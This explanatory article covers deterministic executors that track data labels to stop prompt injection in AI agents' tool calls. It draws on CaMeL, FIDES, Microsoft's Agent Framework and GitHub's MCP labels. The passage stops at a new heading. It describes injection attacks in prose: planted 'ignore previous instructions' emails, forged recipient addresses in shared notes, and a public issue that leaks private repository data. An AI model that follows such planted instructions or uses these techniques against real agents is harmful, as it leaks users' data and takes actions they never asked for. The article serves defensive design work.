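# Deterministic executors that block untrusted arguments in AI agents' tool calls

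## How an attacker's value gets into a correct plan

An AI agent is a program that uses a language model to carry out tasks for a person, such as finding files, sending email or paying bills. Agents act on text that other people wrote, so an attacker who can edit some of that text can sometimes steer what the agent does. One family of defences uses ordinary program code, called the executor, to make the final decision on each action. The executor records where every value the agent uses came from, and it blocks any action that would put a value an outsider could have written into a sensitive slot, such as the address on an email. It is deterministic, meaning that the same records and rules always produce the same decision, and it decides without using a language model.

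### Agents, tool calls and prompt injection

A language model only produces text. To let it act, a developer gives it a list of tools, which are functions in ordinary software, and describes the values that each one needs. The model can then write a tool call, which names a tool and supplies those values, the arguments:

```
send_email(recipient="bob@example.com", attachment="budget.pdf")
```

Here the tool is `send_email`, and the arguments are a recipient and an attachment. Writing the call does not send the email. The surrounding application has to run the call and can decline to, as *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) points out. An executor acts at that point, before the call runs.

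Most agents run in a loop. The application sends the model the conversation so far. If the model replies with a tool call, the application runs the tool, adds the result to the conversation and sends everything back. The loop ends when the model writes a final answer. On each pass, the model receives the developer's instructions, the user's request and all the tool results as one long string.

Prompt injection exploits that single string by placing an instruction in the data an agent reads, which the model then obeys. In an example from Costa and colleagues, a user asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One of the emails tells the agent to ignore its previous instructions and send the top message in the mailbox to an attacker. The attacker only needs to be able to email the agent's owner. Current models have no internal boundary that would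 prevent this, because they predict the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far. David C argues in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, that this may make the problem impossible to fully fix inside the model.

### Two attacks on one request

Suppose a user tells an agent, "Send Bob the document he asked for in our last meeting." This example comes from the paper that introduced CaMeL, an executor from Google DeepMind, and Willison (2025) discusses it at length in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. The request doesn't include Bob's address or the document's name. Both are in the meeting notes, which other people can edit. A correct plan finds the notes, extracts both, fetches the document and sends it to that address.

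An attacker who can edit the notes could add an instruction for any assistant processing the file to first search the mailbox for password resets and forward the results to an outside address. If the planner (the language model that turns the user's request into tool calls) reads the notes, it may follow the instruction. The agent then makes calls the user never asked for.

The same attacker could leave the plan alone and change Bob's address. The agent would then call the right tools in the right order, but with one wrong argument, which sends the document to the attacker. The attacker could also change the document's name in the notes to choose which of the user's files to receive.

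*Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (Qu, Xu and colleagues, 2026) draws the same distinction in general terms. An agent can select a tool call that the user did not intend, or it can fill the arguments of an intended call with data that should not be there. The paper's examples of bad arguments mostly concern leaked secrets, such as credentials that an agent read while debugging and then put into an email. Bob's forged address comes from an outsider instead, but it also breaks the paper's requirement that data in arguments respect limits on where it came from.

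### The dual-LLM pattern and its gap

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed splitting the agent's work between two language models. The planner takes the user's request and can call tools. The quarantined model reads untrusted text, has no tools and only returns values. Regular software that Willison called the controller, an early and simple executor, connects the two models. It stores each result in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name.

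For Bob's document, the planner might write this:

```
notes    = find_notes("last meeting")
doc_name = quarantined_model("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)
address  = quarantined_model("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_document(doc_name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

The executor runs the first line and keeps the text of the notes. For each of the next two lines, it gives the quarantined model that text and a question, then stores whatever the model returns. It then fetches the document and sends it. The planner wrote all five lines knowing only what the user had said. Willison allowed the planner to see an answer from the quarantined model only if ordinary code can first verify that the answer is harmless, for instance by checking that it is one of a fixed list of categories.

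This arrangement stops the first attack. The line about password resets reaches only the quarantined model, which cannot search a mailbox or forward anything. At worst, that model returns a strange string instead of an address. The design does not depend on the quarantined model behaving well, and Willison assumed it could act against the user at any moment.

The second attack gets through. The variable `address` holds whatever the quarantined model returned, and the last line puts it into the email's recipient field. The CaMeL paper pointed this out two years after the original proposal, and Willison accepted that it was a flaw he hadn't known about. In the paper's version, instructions hidden in the notes make the quarantined model return the wrong address. But an attacker may not need instructions. If the notes list the wrong address for Bob, even a quarantined model that works perfectly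 will return it, so using a model that is harder to fool wouldn't prevent this.

Whether an attacker can redirect an email depends on where the agent gets the address. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Willison (2025) reviews the paper of the same name by Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues and repeats its example of a user who asks an agent to send today's schedule to their boss, John Doe. That plan contains John Doe's address from the start, so a malicious calendar entry can corrupt the body of the email but cannot redirect it. In Bob's case, the agent learns the address only by reading a file that an attacker may have edited. Many ordinary requests, such as paying the invoice that arrived this morning, also require the agent to take a value from data that an attacker may have edited.

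### Sources, sinks and taint

Programmers have dealt with a similar problem, SQL injection, for decades. It can occur when a website builds a database query by pasting a visitor's input into its text. A visitor who types a fragment of query language instead of a name can then read or change the database. The usual fix is a parameterised query, in which the programmer sets the structure of the query first and the database treats the input only as a value. David C warns against expecting the same fix for prompt injection, because a language model has no comparable separation between instructions and data.

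The dual-LLM pattern supplies something like that separation from the outside, since the planner fixes the plan before any untrusted text arrives. It also has the limits of a parameterised query, which prevents a value from becoming a command but doesn't ensure that the value is right. If a visitor enters someone else's account number, a correctly parameterised query will look up that account unless another check prevents it. Bob's forged address is likewise a wrong value that contains no command.

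An older technique, taint tracking, follows the values themselves. GitHub's *CodeQL zero to hero part 1* describes injection flaws as untrusted input ending up in a sensitive function. In the standard terms it uses, a source is where data enters the program, and a sink is where a value can do harm. Jana's university lecture slides, *Taint tracking*, divide the job into marking data at the sources, carrying the marks along as the program computes, and checking for them at the sinks.

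The programming language Perl has a built-in taint mode. When a programmer switches it on, Perl marks command-line arguments, environment variables and all file input as tainted. Anything the program computes from a tainted value generally becomes tainted too. If a tainted value reaches a command that starts a shell or modifies a file, the program stops with an error. Perl's designers had to decide which operations were dangerous enough to guard, and they let a program open a file under a tainted name for reading but not for writing. The programmer can clear a mark by matching the value against a pattern of permitted characters. Perl does not check that the pattern is sensible, so a pattern that accepts everything also clears the mark, according to its documentation.

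In an agent, the mark becomes a label attached to each value, which records who could have written the value (its integrity) and who may read it (its confidentiality). A value is tainted if its label shows that an untrusted party could have influenced it. Under the basic rule for combining labels, data derived from both trusted and untrusted inputs counts as untrusted (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026, *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*).

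For agents, the sinks are tool arguments. In Bob's case, the meeting notes are the source and the recipient of `send_email` is the sink. The quarantined model computed `address` from the notes, so `address` inherits their taint, whatever the model did with the text. Just before the email goes out, the executor applies the gate: it checks the taint label against a rule that recipients must be trusted, and blocks the call. CaMeL and FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, both work roughly this way.

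### What the attacker can do

Any guarantee from such a system depends on its threat model, which includes what it assumes about the attacker. Work in this area mostly shares the same threat model. Kolluri and colleagues trust the user, the planner and the software behind the tools, but assume that the data sources may contain injections. The executor must also be trustworthy because it enforces the rules. Trusting the planner mainly means assuming that no attacker has tampered with the model or its instructions. The dual-LLM pattern then keeps the attacker's text away from the planner.

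The attacker in this model is still quite strong. In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) assume an attacker who controls at least one channel that the agent reads, has full knowledge of the defence, and can keep adjusting the attack. The attacker may also see some of what the agent does. Costa and colleagues note that even a web search can leave traces in a site's visitor statistics.

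Researchers agree less about which data to distrust. Costa and colleagues give a corporate database as an example of a trusted source, while Narisetty and colleagues treat every tool result as untrusted. Meeting notes that only coworkers can edit might be trusted under the first approach but not the second.

Several real dangers lie outside the model altogether:

- **Poisoned tools.** The planner reads the tool descriptions as part of its prompt, so a malicious description would reach it directly. A malicious tool could also ignore its arguments and do something else entirely. Qu and colleagues cite a campaign called ClawHavoc, which planted over 1,000 malicious add-ons in a public marketplace for agent software, and they argue that trusting tools no longer makes sense where users install such add-ons themselves.
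- **The user.** A malicious user can simply ask for the harmful action. An honest one can paste in text from an attacker, which the agent will then treat as the user's own words, a weakness that Willison acknowledged in his original proposal.
- **Honest mistakes.** Costa and colleagues point out that models misread requests even when all the data is trustworthy. If the user's own address book contains two Bobs and the planner picks the wrong one, the address carries a trusted label and the gate lets it through.
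- **Biased judgement.** A paper that praises itself might sway an agent that is reviewing it, as Qu and colleagues observe, without causing a single improper tool call.

### Why the check should not ask a model

Defences that rely on a language model to spot attacks, either by training the planner to resist them or by adding a second model as a filter, are simpler but work only some of the time, and an attacker can keep trying. Willison argues that a filter which catches 99% of attacks is a failure by the standards of application security, because attackers will look for the other 1%. Narisetty and colleagues quote Anthropic's figures for one of its earlier models, Claude Opus 4.5, in coding tasks. Attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred.

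Published results for model-level defences have also tended to overstate how well the defences work. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) adapted their attacks to 12 defences against prompt injection or jailbreaks (users' own attempts to get around a model's restrictions). The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences, although the success rates originally reported for the majority were near zero. On a subset of cases where an automated search succeeded 69% of the time, human testers collectively succeeded every time. One message that got past a detector merely claimed that company policy required staff to log calendar changes by deleting a certain file.

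Narisetty and colleagues still see value in model-level defences as one layer among several. They also caution that researchers have tested deterministic executors mostly against fixed sets of attacks, so confidence in those may be premature too. But the second attack on Bob's request gives a more specific reason not to leave the decision to a model. If the attacker has only swapped one address for another, the notes contain no instruction for a filter to find, and the forged address may look as ordinary as the real one. The executor can still establish that the address came from a file that other people can edit, because ordinary code can record that without interpreting the text. However, Bob's real address comes from the same file, so a gate that accepts only trusted recipients will also block the legitimate email when nobody has tampered with the notes.

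## Choosing the sensitive arguments and labelling the data

The gate blocks Bob's real address along with the forged one because the developer told the executor that an email's recipient must be trusted and that the meeting notes are untrusted. Before the agent runs, a developer has to decide which arguments of each tool must be trusted and whether each data source is trusted. An attacker can exploit sensitive arguments left unguarded, but guarding too many arguments stops the agent from doing ordinary work.

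### Going through the tools one argument at a time

Some tools need no guard. Kolluri and colleagues sorted the twelve tools of a web-browsing agent into seven that can change something, such as clicking, typing and opening an address, and five that could run at any time, such as scrolling and hovering. They assumed that an attacker could not make these five do anything else on the two test sites, copies of GitLab and Reddit. On a page that submits a form when the pointer passes over it, hovering would need a guard too.

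For each remaining tool, the developer can ask what an attacker would gain by choosing the value of each argument.

| Tool | Argument | Must it be trusted? | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| `send_email` | `to`, `cc` | Yes | These decide who receives everything else in the message. |
| | `bcc` | Yes | As above, and the other recipients cannot see the extra address. |
| | `body` | No | Every recipient must have permission to read it, but an outsider may have written parts of it. |
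| | `attachments` | The choice of file, yes; its contents, no | An attacker who can name the file can pick which one leaves. |
| `transfer` | `payee` | Yes | This decides who gets the money. |
| | `amount` | Yes | The right payee with the wrong amount still costs the user money. |
| `write_file` | `path` | Yes | A bad path could overwrite a script or a settings file. |
| | `content` | Depends on the path | Outside text is fine in a file of notes, but not in a file that a program will later run. |
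| `create_event` | `participants` | Yes | Calendars usually send participants an invitation, so this is a list of recipients. |

An email tool can accept a tainted body but not a tainted recipient, because whoever chooses the recipient chooses where the user's data goes. Someone who influences the body can mislead the reader, but the reader is still the person the user picked. Requiring trusted bodies would also rule out most useful email tasks, since nearly all summaries, replies and forwarded messages contain somebody else's words. Costa and colleagues make the same distinction and accept its drawback, which is that if a user asks for a summary of three emails, one malicious email could make the summary come out empty. A developer who can't tolerate that can require a trusted body for that tool. Links in the body need a separate check, because opening one can send data to an outside server.

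Attachments are awkward because one label has to cover both the file's contents and the choice of file. In Bob's case, `document` is tainted if an outsider could have written the file or could have chosen it by changing the name in the notes. By the time the file reaches `send_email`, the label no longer shows which of these applies. The developer can guard the choice earlier, at `fetch_document(doc_name)`, or can require that every recipient already has permission to read the file.

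Not every system can treat arguments separately. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes a file-writing tool that won't run if either the path or the text comes from an untrusted source. The tool is part of an example for Microsoft's Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents that includes an experimental version of FIDES. An agent with this tool could not save a summary of a web page, even to a file the user had named.

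Costa and colleagues' own tests had the opposite weakness. Their formal model labels each argument, but the trusted-call check they ran on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking, travel and chat tasks, did not use those labels. It tested only whether the planner had chosen the call in a trusted context. The tools for sending money and scheduling payments had no other check, so a payee that the quarantined model had copied from a forged invoice would have passed. Bob's forged address would also have passed, because the planner never reads the notes and its context therefore stays trusted. The tests are good evidence about injected calls but provide little evidence about swapped values.

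### Labels and how they combine

Labels need an order, so that the executor can compare them, and a rule for combining them. Write `x ⊑ y` if label `y` is at least as restrictive as label `x`. The join of two labels, written `x ⊔ y`, is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both. A set of labels in which every pair has a join is, loosely, a lattice. (Strictly, a lattice also needs a greatest lower bound for every pair, which the executor never uses.)

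The smallest useful lattice for integrity has two labels, trusted (T) and untrusted (U), with `T ⊑ U`. Combining trusted and untrusted data gives untrusted data (`T ⊔ U = U`), which is the basic taint rule. Confidentiality has a matching pair, public (L, for low) and secret (H, for high), with `L ⊑ H`. Developers can add levels. For example, Microsoft's Agent Framework has public, private, and a top level for credentials and personal data.

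A list of permitted readers carries more information than a level does. Suppose A, B and C may read one document, and B, C and D may read another. Only B and C may read a text that draws on both:

```
{A,B,C} ⊔ {B,C,D}  =  {A,B,C} ∩ {B,C,D}  =  {B,C}
```

A label with fewer readers is more restrictive and ranks higher in the order, so `{A,B,C} ⊑ {B,C}`. Integrity labels can also be sets, listing possible writers, and they combine by union. If A, B and C could have edited one document and B, C and D the other, any of the four could have influenced the combined text.

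A full label is a pair of an integrity label and a confidentiality label, in that order, and the executor joins each component separately. The bottom of the lattice is (T, L), trusted public data that can go anywhere. The top is (U, H), secret data that an outsider may have influenced.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* works through a case for reader sets in which nobody is attacking anything. Alex asks an agent to deal with the unanswered emails in an inbox. One email is from Priya and contains a preview of the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but isn't allowed to see them yet. The readers of each email are its sender and its recipient, so once the agent has read both, anything it writes has this label:

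```
{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco}  =  {Alex}
```

Marco isn't in the set, so the executor won't send him a reply without confirmation. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the result would have been `{Alex, Marco}` and the executor could have sent the reply.

For the same reason, the agent can't reply to Priya either, even if the reply mentions only her own figures. The reply's label reflects everything the agent had read before writing it, including anything the agent didn't use. Handling the two emails in separate runs would avoid the problem.

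### Trusted action and permitted flow

Two rules cover most of what a gate has to check. The trusted action rule allows a call only if the planner chose it in a trusted context and its sensitive arguments are trusted. The permitted flow rule allows data to leave only if every recipient is allowed to read it.

Kolluri and colleagues write both as upper limits on labels. A proposed call to a tool `f` has one label for the context in which the planner chose it and one for each argument. The developer sets a limit for each, and the call passes if no label exceeds its limit:

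```
call:      f(a1, ..., an), with labels  ℓ  (context)  and  ℓ1, ..., ℓn  (arguments)
limits:    π  (context)  and  π1, ..., πn  (arguments)
allowed:   ℓ ⊑ π,  and  ℓi ⊑ πi  for every argument
```

The symbol ⊤ stands for the most restrictive label, so a limit of ⊤ accepts anything. The two rules are then:

```
trusted action:   π = (T, ⊤),  and  πi = (T, ⊤)  for each argument that must be trusted
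permitted flow:   for send(R, d), which sends data d to recipients R:   πd = (⊤, R)
```

Larger reader sets rank lower in the order, so the permitted-flow limit holds exactly when every member of R is a permitted reader of `d`. Costa and colleagues describe a stricter version of trusted action that requires every argument to be trusted, which would block an email with a tainted body. Kolluri and colleagues let the developer choose the arguments, and the table of tools above shows one way to choose them.

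The trusted action rule alone stops both attacks on Bob's request. It blocks the call if the planner tries to forward password resets after reading the notes, because its context is then tainted, and also if the planner's context is untainted but the recipient's address came from the notes, because the address is tainted. However, the rule doesn't check who may read the data, so it won't stop an agent that misunderstands an honest request and sends salary figures to the wrong colleague.

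Permitted flow on its own limits the damage an injection can do but doesn't prevent the injection, because it doesn't check why the planner chose the call. A planner that has followed an attacker's instruction can't deliver data to anyone outside the reader set, but it can still send messages the user never asked for, as long as every recipient was entitled to the contents. It can also delete files or cancel meetings, since those calls don't send data to anyone. Costa and colleagues saw milder examples in their tests, where the policies allowed injected instructions to create a calendar event with no participants and to post a message to a chat channel whose members were all allowed to read its contents.

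A developer can require both rules or accept a call that satisfies either. These options can give different results for tools that send data. In the last two rows below, the user's request is genuine and the recipient's address is trusted.

| Situation | Trusted action only | Permitted flow only | Either is enough | Both required |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| An injected instruction sends a private file to an outsider | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |
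| An injected instruction messages people who may already read the contents | Blocked | Allowed | Allowed | Blocked |
| The agent misreads a request and sends private data to the wrong colleague | Allowed | Blocked | Allowed | Blocked |
| The user deliberately shares a document with a new reader | Allowed | Blocked | Allowed | Blocked |

Requiring both gives the strongest guarantee, but it prevents the agent from sharing anything with a new person on its own, which is often the purpose of an email. Kolluri and colleagues accept either rule for tools that send data and require trusted action for other tools with consequences. Security researchers call the result robust declassification. Declassifying data means releasing it to people outside its reader set, and the release is robust if an attacker can't trigger it. Honest mistakes can still get through. If Alex's company treated emails between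 colleagues as trusted, accepting either rule would let the reply with the sales figures go to Marco.

Accepting either rule also lets the executor send Bob the document when his address came from the notes, provided he already has permission to open it. An outsider's forged address would fail the same check, so at worst the attacker could redirect the document to someone else who could already open it. If the user is sharing the document with Bob for the first time, he isn't in the reader set yet, and the executor needs a trusted source for his address.

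### Where labels come from

Both rules depend on correct labels, which somebody has to assign. The coarsest method is to label a whole tool. For example, a developer might label everything a web-fetching tool returns as untrusted, which takes one line and is nearly always correct.

Labelling each result separately suits tools whose data varies. Microsoft's example is a tool that reads issues, which are bug reports and requests filed on a GitHub repository. The tool's code marks every issue as untrusted, because anyone may have written it, and as public or private depending on its repository. If a result has its own label, the Agent Framework uses that. Otherwise it uses the tool's declared label, or, if there is none, combines the labels of the tool's inputs.

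Labels on individual fields are finer still. Tools usually return structured data, such as an email with separate fields for sender, date, subject and body. Costa and colleagues allow a label at any level of that structure, and the label applies to everything beneath it. Kolluri and colleagues similarly label parts of a web page, treating text posted by users as untrusted and the site's own buttons and text boxes as trusted. The planner can then receive the page's controls without the users' text.

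Field labels require more thought about what "trusted" means. Costa and colleagues suggest that an email's sender address could count as trusted when the mail server has authenticated it with DMARC, a standard for checking that a message comes from the domain it claims. That establishes who sent the email, but an attacker writing from their own genuine account also passes the check. If the agent plans to reply to the latest message with a confidential file, the sender's authentication doesn't justify sending it.

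In their tests, Costa and colleagues used a simpler method, marking a field untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark targeted it. This gave them a clear baseline, but the labels depend on where the benchmark's attacks are, not on who could have written each field. One banking task asked the agent to change the user's password if it found a suspicious transaction. The executor hid the subject lines, which were labelled untrusted. The amounts and dates were labelled trusted, and the planner changed the password after seeing a large amount. Yet anyone who sends the user money chooses the amount. A number can hardly carry an injected instruction, but here it was enough to determine whether a sensitive call happened.

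Reader sets often have to be guessed. Costa and colleagues took the readers of an email to be its sender and recipients, while noting that people may have shared it more widely. Leaving out readers is a fairly safe error, because it blocks legitimate emails but doesn't leak anything.

### Carrying labels between agents and tools

Many agents get their tools from separate programs, called servers, through an open standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP). A server often has information about its data that the agent lacks, such as who belongs to a chat channel. A Microsoft prototype lets servers pass this information along as labels. It puts the labels in `_meta`, an optional metadata field in MCP messages, for both tool calls and results. Software that doesn't support the labels can ignore them and work as before.

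Each label specifies the part of the message it applies to in a notation called JSONPath. The path `$` means the whole message, and `$.arguments.content` means only the `content` argument. In Microsoft's example, an agent tries to post a note about a product announcement to a channel in Teams, the company's workplace chat program. The call as a whole is labelled untrusted and public. The text of the note has its own label, which marks it as trusted and lists two people who may read it.

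#### GitHub's labels

GitHub worked with Microsoft to add labels to its MCP server. The server labels files and issues from public repositories as untrusted and public, and those from private repositories as trusted and private. The labels address an attack that researchers had already demonstrated, in which someone opens an issue in a public repository asking for information from a private one. An agent working for a user with access to both reads the issue, fetches the private data and posts it as a public comment.

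With labels in place, the agent's context becomes untrusted when it reads the issue and private when it reads the private files. The policy forbids the agent from posting publicly once its context is both. An agent that works only in public repositories, or only in private ones, never combines the two and can finish without interruption. GitHub's command-line agent, Copilot CLI, has experimental support for these checks, but only for selected tools from GitHub's own server.

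A single "private" label doesn't distinguish between two private repositories, so this policy wouldn't stop data from moving between repositories with different members. *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from GitHub's research group GitHub Next, describes a finer scheme in which a label is a set of tags and each tag can name one repository. An agent can read from a repository only if the agent's label already includes that repository's tag.

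#### A policy for a Teams message, line by line

In Microsoft's prototype, a server can also publish the policy for each of its tools. The policies are in Rego, a language for writing access rules, and each one returns a decision to allow the call, deny it or ask a person. The published policy for sending a Teams message works as follows:

1. `default decision` is a denial, so a call fails if nothing later produces a decision.
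2. `allow`, `deny` and `ask` are small helper functions that attach a message to each kind of decision.
3. `context_trusted` is true if the label on `$`, the whole call, is trusted.
4. `content_readers` is the set of people who may read the text, taken from the label on `$.arguments.content`.
5. `members` comes from a live request to the Teams server for the channel's current members. Microsoft extended Rego to permit such lookups, but only through tools that change nothing and don't reach beyond the server.
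6. `target_user_ids` and `allowed_user_ids` hold the IDs of the channel's members and of the permitted readers.
7. `missing` is the difference between those two sets, which leaves the members who may not read the text.
8. `msg` lists the missing members, in case a person has to decide.
9. `decision` allows the call if the context is trusted. If it isn't, the policy allows the call when `missing` is empty, and otherwise asks a person. A final branch denies the call.

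For the announcement, the context is untrusted, so the outcome depends on who is in the channel. The message goes out if the two permitted readers are the only members, but a person has to decide if there is a third member.

The condition for asking a person is that the number of missing members is at least zero, which is true of any count. The final denial therefore seems to apply only when the policy can't compute the number, for instance because the membership lookup failed.

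This is an either-rule, with trusted action checked first. The policy checks the labels on the whole call and on the text, but not the label on `channelId`, which decides where the message goes. Copilot CLI labels the whole call based on the planner's context. Suppose a client that does this has a clean context and passes along a channel ID that the quarantined model took from an outsider's document. The policy would allow the message without comparing the channel's members with the permitted readers, which is the same mistake as sending Bob's document to a forged address. Requiring a trusted label on `$.arguments.channelId` before the first branch applies would fix this.

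#### Defaults for tools without labels

Most MCP servers don't supply labels. Microsoft has released a gateway that sits between the agent and such a server and adds labels. For each tool, however, a developer must describe the structure of its results, write a function that computes their labels, and write or choose a policy.

An option that takes less work is to use hints that servers can already attach to their tools, such as whether a tool only reads data, whether it deals with an open-ended outside world, and whether it can destroy something. Microsoft suggests that an executor could always allow a tool that only reads from a closed system. A tool that reads from the open world, such as a web search, would run only if all its arguments were public, because the search terms leave the agent. Destructive tools might always need a person's approval. To label results, the executor would assume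 that any argument could end up in them. It would also mark results from open-world tools as untrusted and results from tools that require a login as private.

These defaults depend on the hints being accurate and on the developer interpreting them correctly. The hints also don't record who wrote the data. A server might reasonably describe a shared notes folder as a closed system, since reading it contacts nothing outside. The notes, including Bob's forged address, would then not be labelled untrusted.

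### Labelling errors and how to repair them

Narisetty and colleagues argue that everything else depends on the initial assignment of labels, and that none of the systems they surveyed specifies it well enough. They relied on the systems' own descriptions and did not measure how often labels are wrong. But an executor applies a label even if it is wrong, and four labelling errors are easy to foresee.

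The simplest labelling error is to leave a tool unlabelled when the executor trusts unlabelled output. In May 2026, Microsoft warned that the Agent Framework treated such output as trusted and public, and asked users whether they would prefer a stricter default. The framework's documentation instead gives the default as untrusted and public, so developers should check what their installed version does. Treating unlabelled output as untrusted and public protects integrity but not confidentiality. If a developer forgets to label a tool that reads payroll records, its output still counts as public and could end up in a public comment. Developers can change both defaults, and the cautious setting is untrusted and private.

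The fallback of combining input labels can cause the same error. It works for a summariser, whose output is only as trustworthy as the text it was given. But it mislabels web pages fetched by a tool, because a trusted search term would cause the page to be labelled trusted too. Microsoft recommends declaring a label on any tool that brings in outside data.

The framework also has a dry-run mode, which tracks labels and records what the gate would have blocked, without blocking it. This is a good way to find labels that are too strict, but it won't reveal labels that are too lax, because a tainted value marked as trusted never triggers a block. A start-up check that rejects any tool without a declared label would catch missing labels.

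Text that the user pastes in is harder to deal with, because the executor treats it as the user's own words. Costa and colleagues give user messages the bottom label by default, which makes them public as well as trusted, so a password that the user types is not protected from being leaked. Their design allows a different label on any message. An application that can tell pasted or attached text from typed text could label the pasted or attached text as untrusted and hide it from the planner like any other outside data. This would sometimes label text as untrusted when it should be trusted, since users also paste addresses they have checked and intend to use.

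A private store can also contain text from outsiders. Private repositories hold customers' bug reports, copied error logs and code from other projects, but GitHub's server labels all of it as trusted. It bases the label on who can read the repository, when it should consider who could have written the text. Bob's meeting notes have the same problem if only coworkers can open them but one coworker has pasted in an email from a client. The issue-reading tool in Microsoft's example more safely marks every issue as untrusted, even in a private repository.

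The fix is to label data by who wrote it, ideally for each field or entry, and to use the set of all its writers where the store keeps an edit history. But an edit history records only who saved the text, so an entry that a coworker pasted from elsewhere would still look like the coworker's own. Costa and colleagues also mention upgrading a document from untrusted to trusted after a prompt-injection detector clears it, but they warn that relying on such detectors can weaken the guarantee. A detector would also miss a swapped address like Bob's.

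Labels can also disappear when an agent saves data and reads it back later. Suppose the agent copies Bob's address from the notes into its long-term memory, and a later task retrieves it. If the memory stored the address without its label, the executor treats it as coming from the agent's own records, which a developer may well have labelled as trusted. An address that an attacker put in the notes would then count as trusted, and correcting the notes wouldn't remove it from memory.

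Costa and colleagues' formal model avoids this by keeping a label for everything in storage. When a tool writes a value, the stored label combines the labels of the call, its arguments and any stored data that the tool read. A real memory has to save the label next to the value, where the agent's tools can't edit the label. The storage also needs protection. Microsoft warns that loading a saved session from an untrusted source amounts to accepting untrusted input, because someone who tampers with the storage could change a message's recorded role, for example to make a tool's output appear to come from the developer.

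Databases raise a similar problem. Columbia DAPLab has built a system that enforces rules about which records a table's data may come from. In its example, a tax agent may add an expense only if it derives the expense from an actual receipt. The lab is still working on enforcing these rules across several agent turns, such as when the agent first copies the receipts into an intermediate table and then fills in the expenses from there.

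Narisetty and colleagues treat all saved memory as untrusted in their threat model. This is safe and needs no extra storage, but the agent can't use saved information even if it came directly from the user. If the user typed in Bob's address last month and asked the agent to remember it, the gate would block that address too.

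## Running the plan and checking each call

At each step of the plan, the executor looks up the values behind the variable names, checks their labels against the tool's rule, and either makes the call or refuses it. It stores each result under a new name, with a label that combines the labels of everything that went into it.

### The executor's loop

```
memory = {}                                # name -> (value, label)

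for each step  "name = tool(arguments)"  in the plan:

    for each argument:
        if it is a variable name:   (value, label) = memory[that name]
        if it is a literal:         (value, label) = (the literal, call_label)

    if the tool's rule rejects call_label or any argument's label:
        refuse the step

    result, source_label = tool(values)
    memory[name] = (result, source_label ⊔ call_label ⊔ every argument's label)
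```

`call_label` covers everything the planner had read when it wrote the step. A literal is a value the planner typed into the plan, such as `"last meeting"`. It gets the same label as the call, since the planner could have taken it from anything it had read. In the plan for Bob's document, the planner has read only the user's words, so `call_label` is trusted for every step.

The executor substitutes the real values before it checks the rule, because some rules need them. To check permitted flow, for example, it compares the actual recipients with the people who may read the data.

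In the last line, the executor assumes that every input affected the result, because it can't see how the tool produced it. It treats the quarantined model as another tool, so the model's answers get the label of the notes. If the plan's language has other operations, such as joining two strings or picking an item from a list, the executor has to combine labels there too. Otherwise, adding a space to the end of a tainted address would produce an address labeled clean.

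Costa and colleagues use nearly the same loop in their formal model, which ends the run when a call fails the check. In their tests, the executor instead returned the violation to the planner as the call's result, so the planner could try something else.

### Bob's request, step by step

Suppose outsiders can edit the meeting notes, and Ana, Bob and the user can read them. The document is `budget.pdf`, which the user wrote and nobody else can open yet. The gate on `send_email` accepts a call that meets either the trusted action condition, with `to` as the guarded argument, or the permitted flow condition. Read-only tools have no guard.

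| Step | What the executor runs | Label of the result | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `notes = find_notes("last meeting")` | (U, {user, Ana, Bob}) | Outsiders can edit the notes, and three people can read them. |
| 2 | `doc_name = quarantined_model("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)` | (U, {user, Ana, Bob}) | The answer inherits the label of the notes. |
| 3 | `address = quarantined_model("What is Bob's email address?", notes)` | (U, {user, Ana, Bob}) | As in step 2. |
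| 4 | `document = fetch_document(doc_name)` | (U, {user}) | Only the user can read the file, and the notes determined which file it was. |
| 5 | `send_email(to=address, attachments=document)` | Refused | `to` is untrusted, and the recipient may not yet read the document. |

Now suppose the user adds, "His address is bob@example.com." The planner no longer needs step 3 and types the address into the last step:

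```
send_email(to="bob@example.com", attachments=document)
```

The address is now a literal in a plan that the planner wrote from the user's words alone, so the address is labeled trusted. The call satisfies the trusted action policy and the email goes out, even though Bob couldn't open the document before.

The attachment is still tainted in the second run, so an attacker could change which file Bob gets. If the developer guarded the name passed to `fetch_document`, the executor would stop both runs at that step, and the user would have to specify the file as well as the address.

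### Why one message taints everything in an ordinary agent

The second run succeeds because the planner never reads the notes. In an ordinary agent, every tool result goes straight into the planner's context. The executor then has to keep a context label that combines the labels of all messages so far, and `call_label` equals that label at each step. Once the agent has read the notes, its context is untrusted, and so is every argument it writes afterward, including `bob@example.com`, even though the user typed it.

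The executor has no exact way to tell which message an argument came from. In ordinary software, the source code shows how each output depends on the inputs, but a language model reads its whole context at once, and any part of it could have influenced the next call. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) describes how this worsens an old problem called label creep, in which restrictive labels spread to more and more data until the system blocks harmless actions or keeps asking the user to confirm them.

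The order of the calls therefore matters, and so does avoiding unnecessary ones. In one test by Costa and colleagues, the user's request already named the chat channel to use, but the planner listed all the channels anyway, which lowered the integrity of its context for no benefit. The integrity label then stays low for the rest of the run, because the text that lowered it stays in the context.

An executor can avoid this by keeping tainted text out of the planner's context. CaMeL and FIDES both do so, but they differ in when the planner decides what to do.

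### CaMeL writes the whole program first

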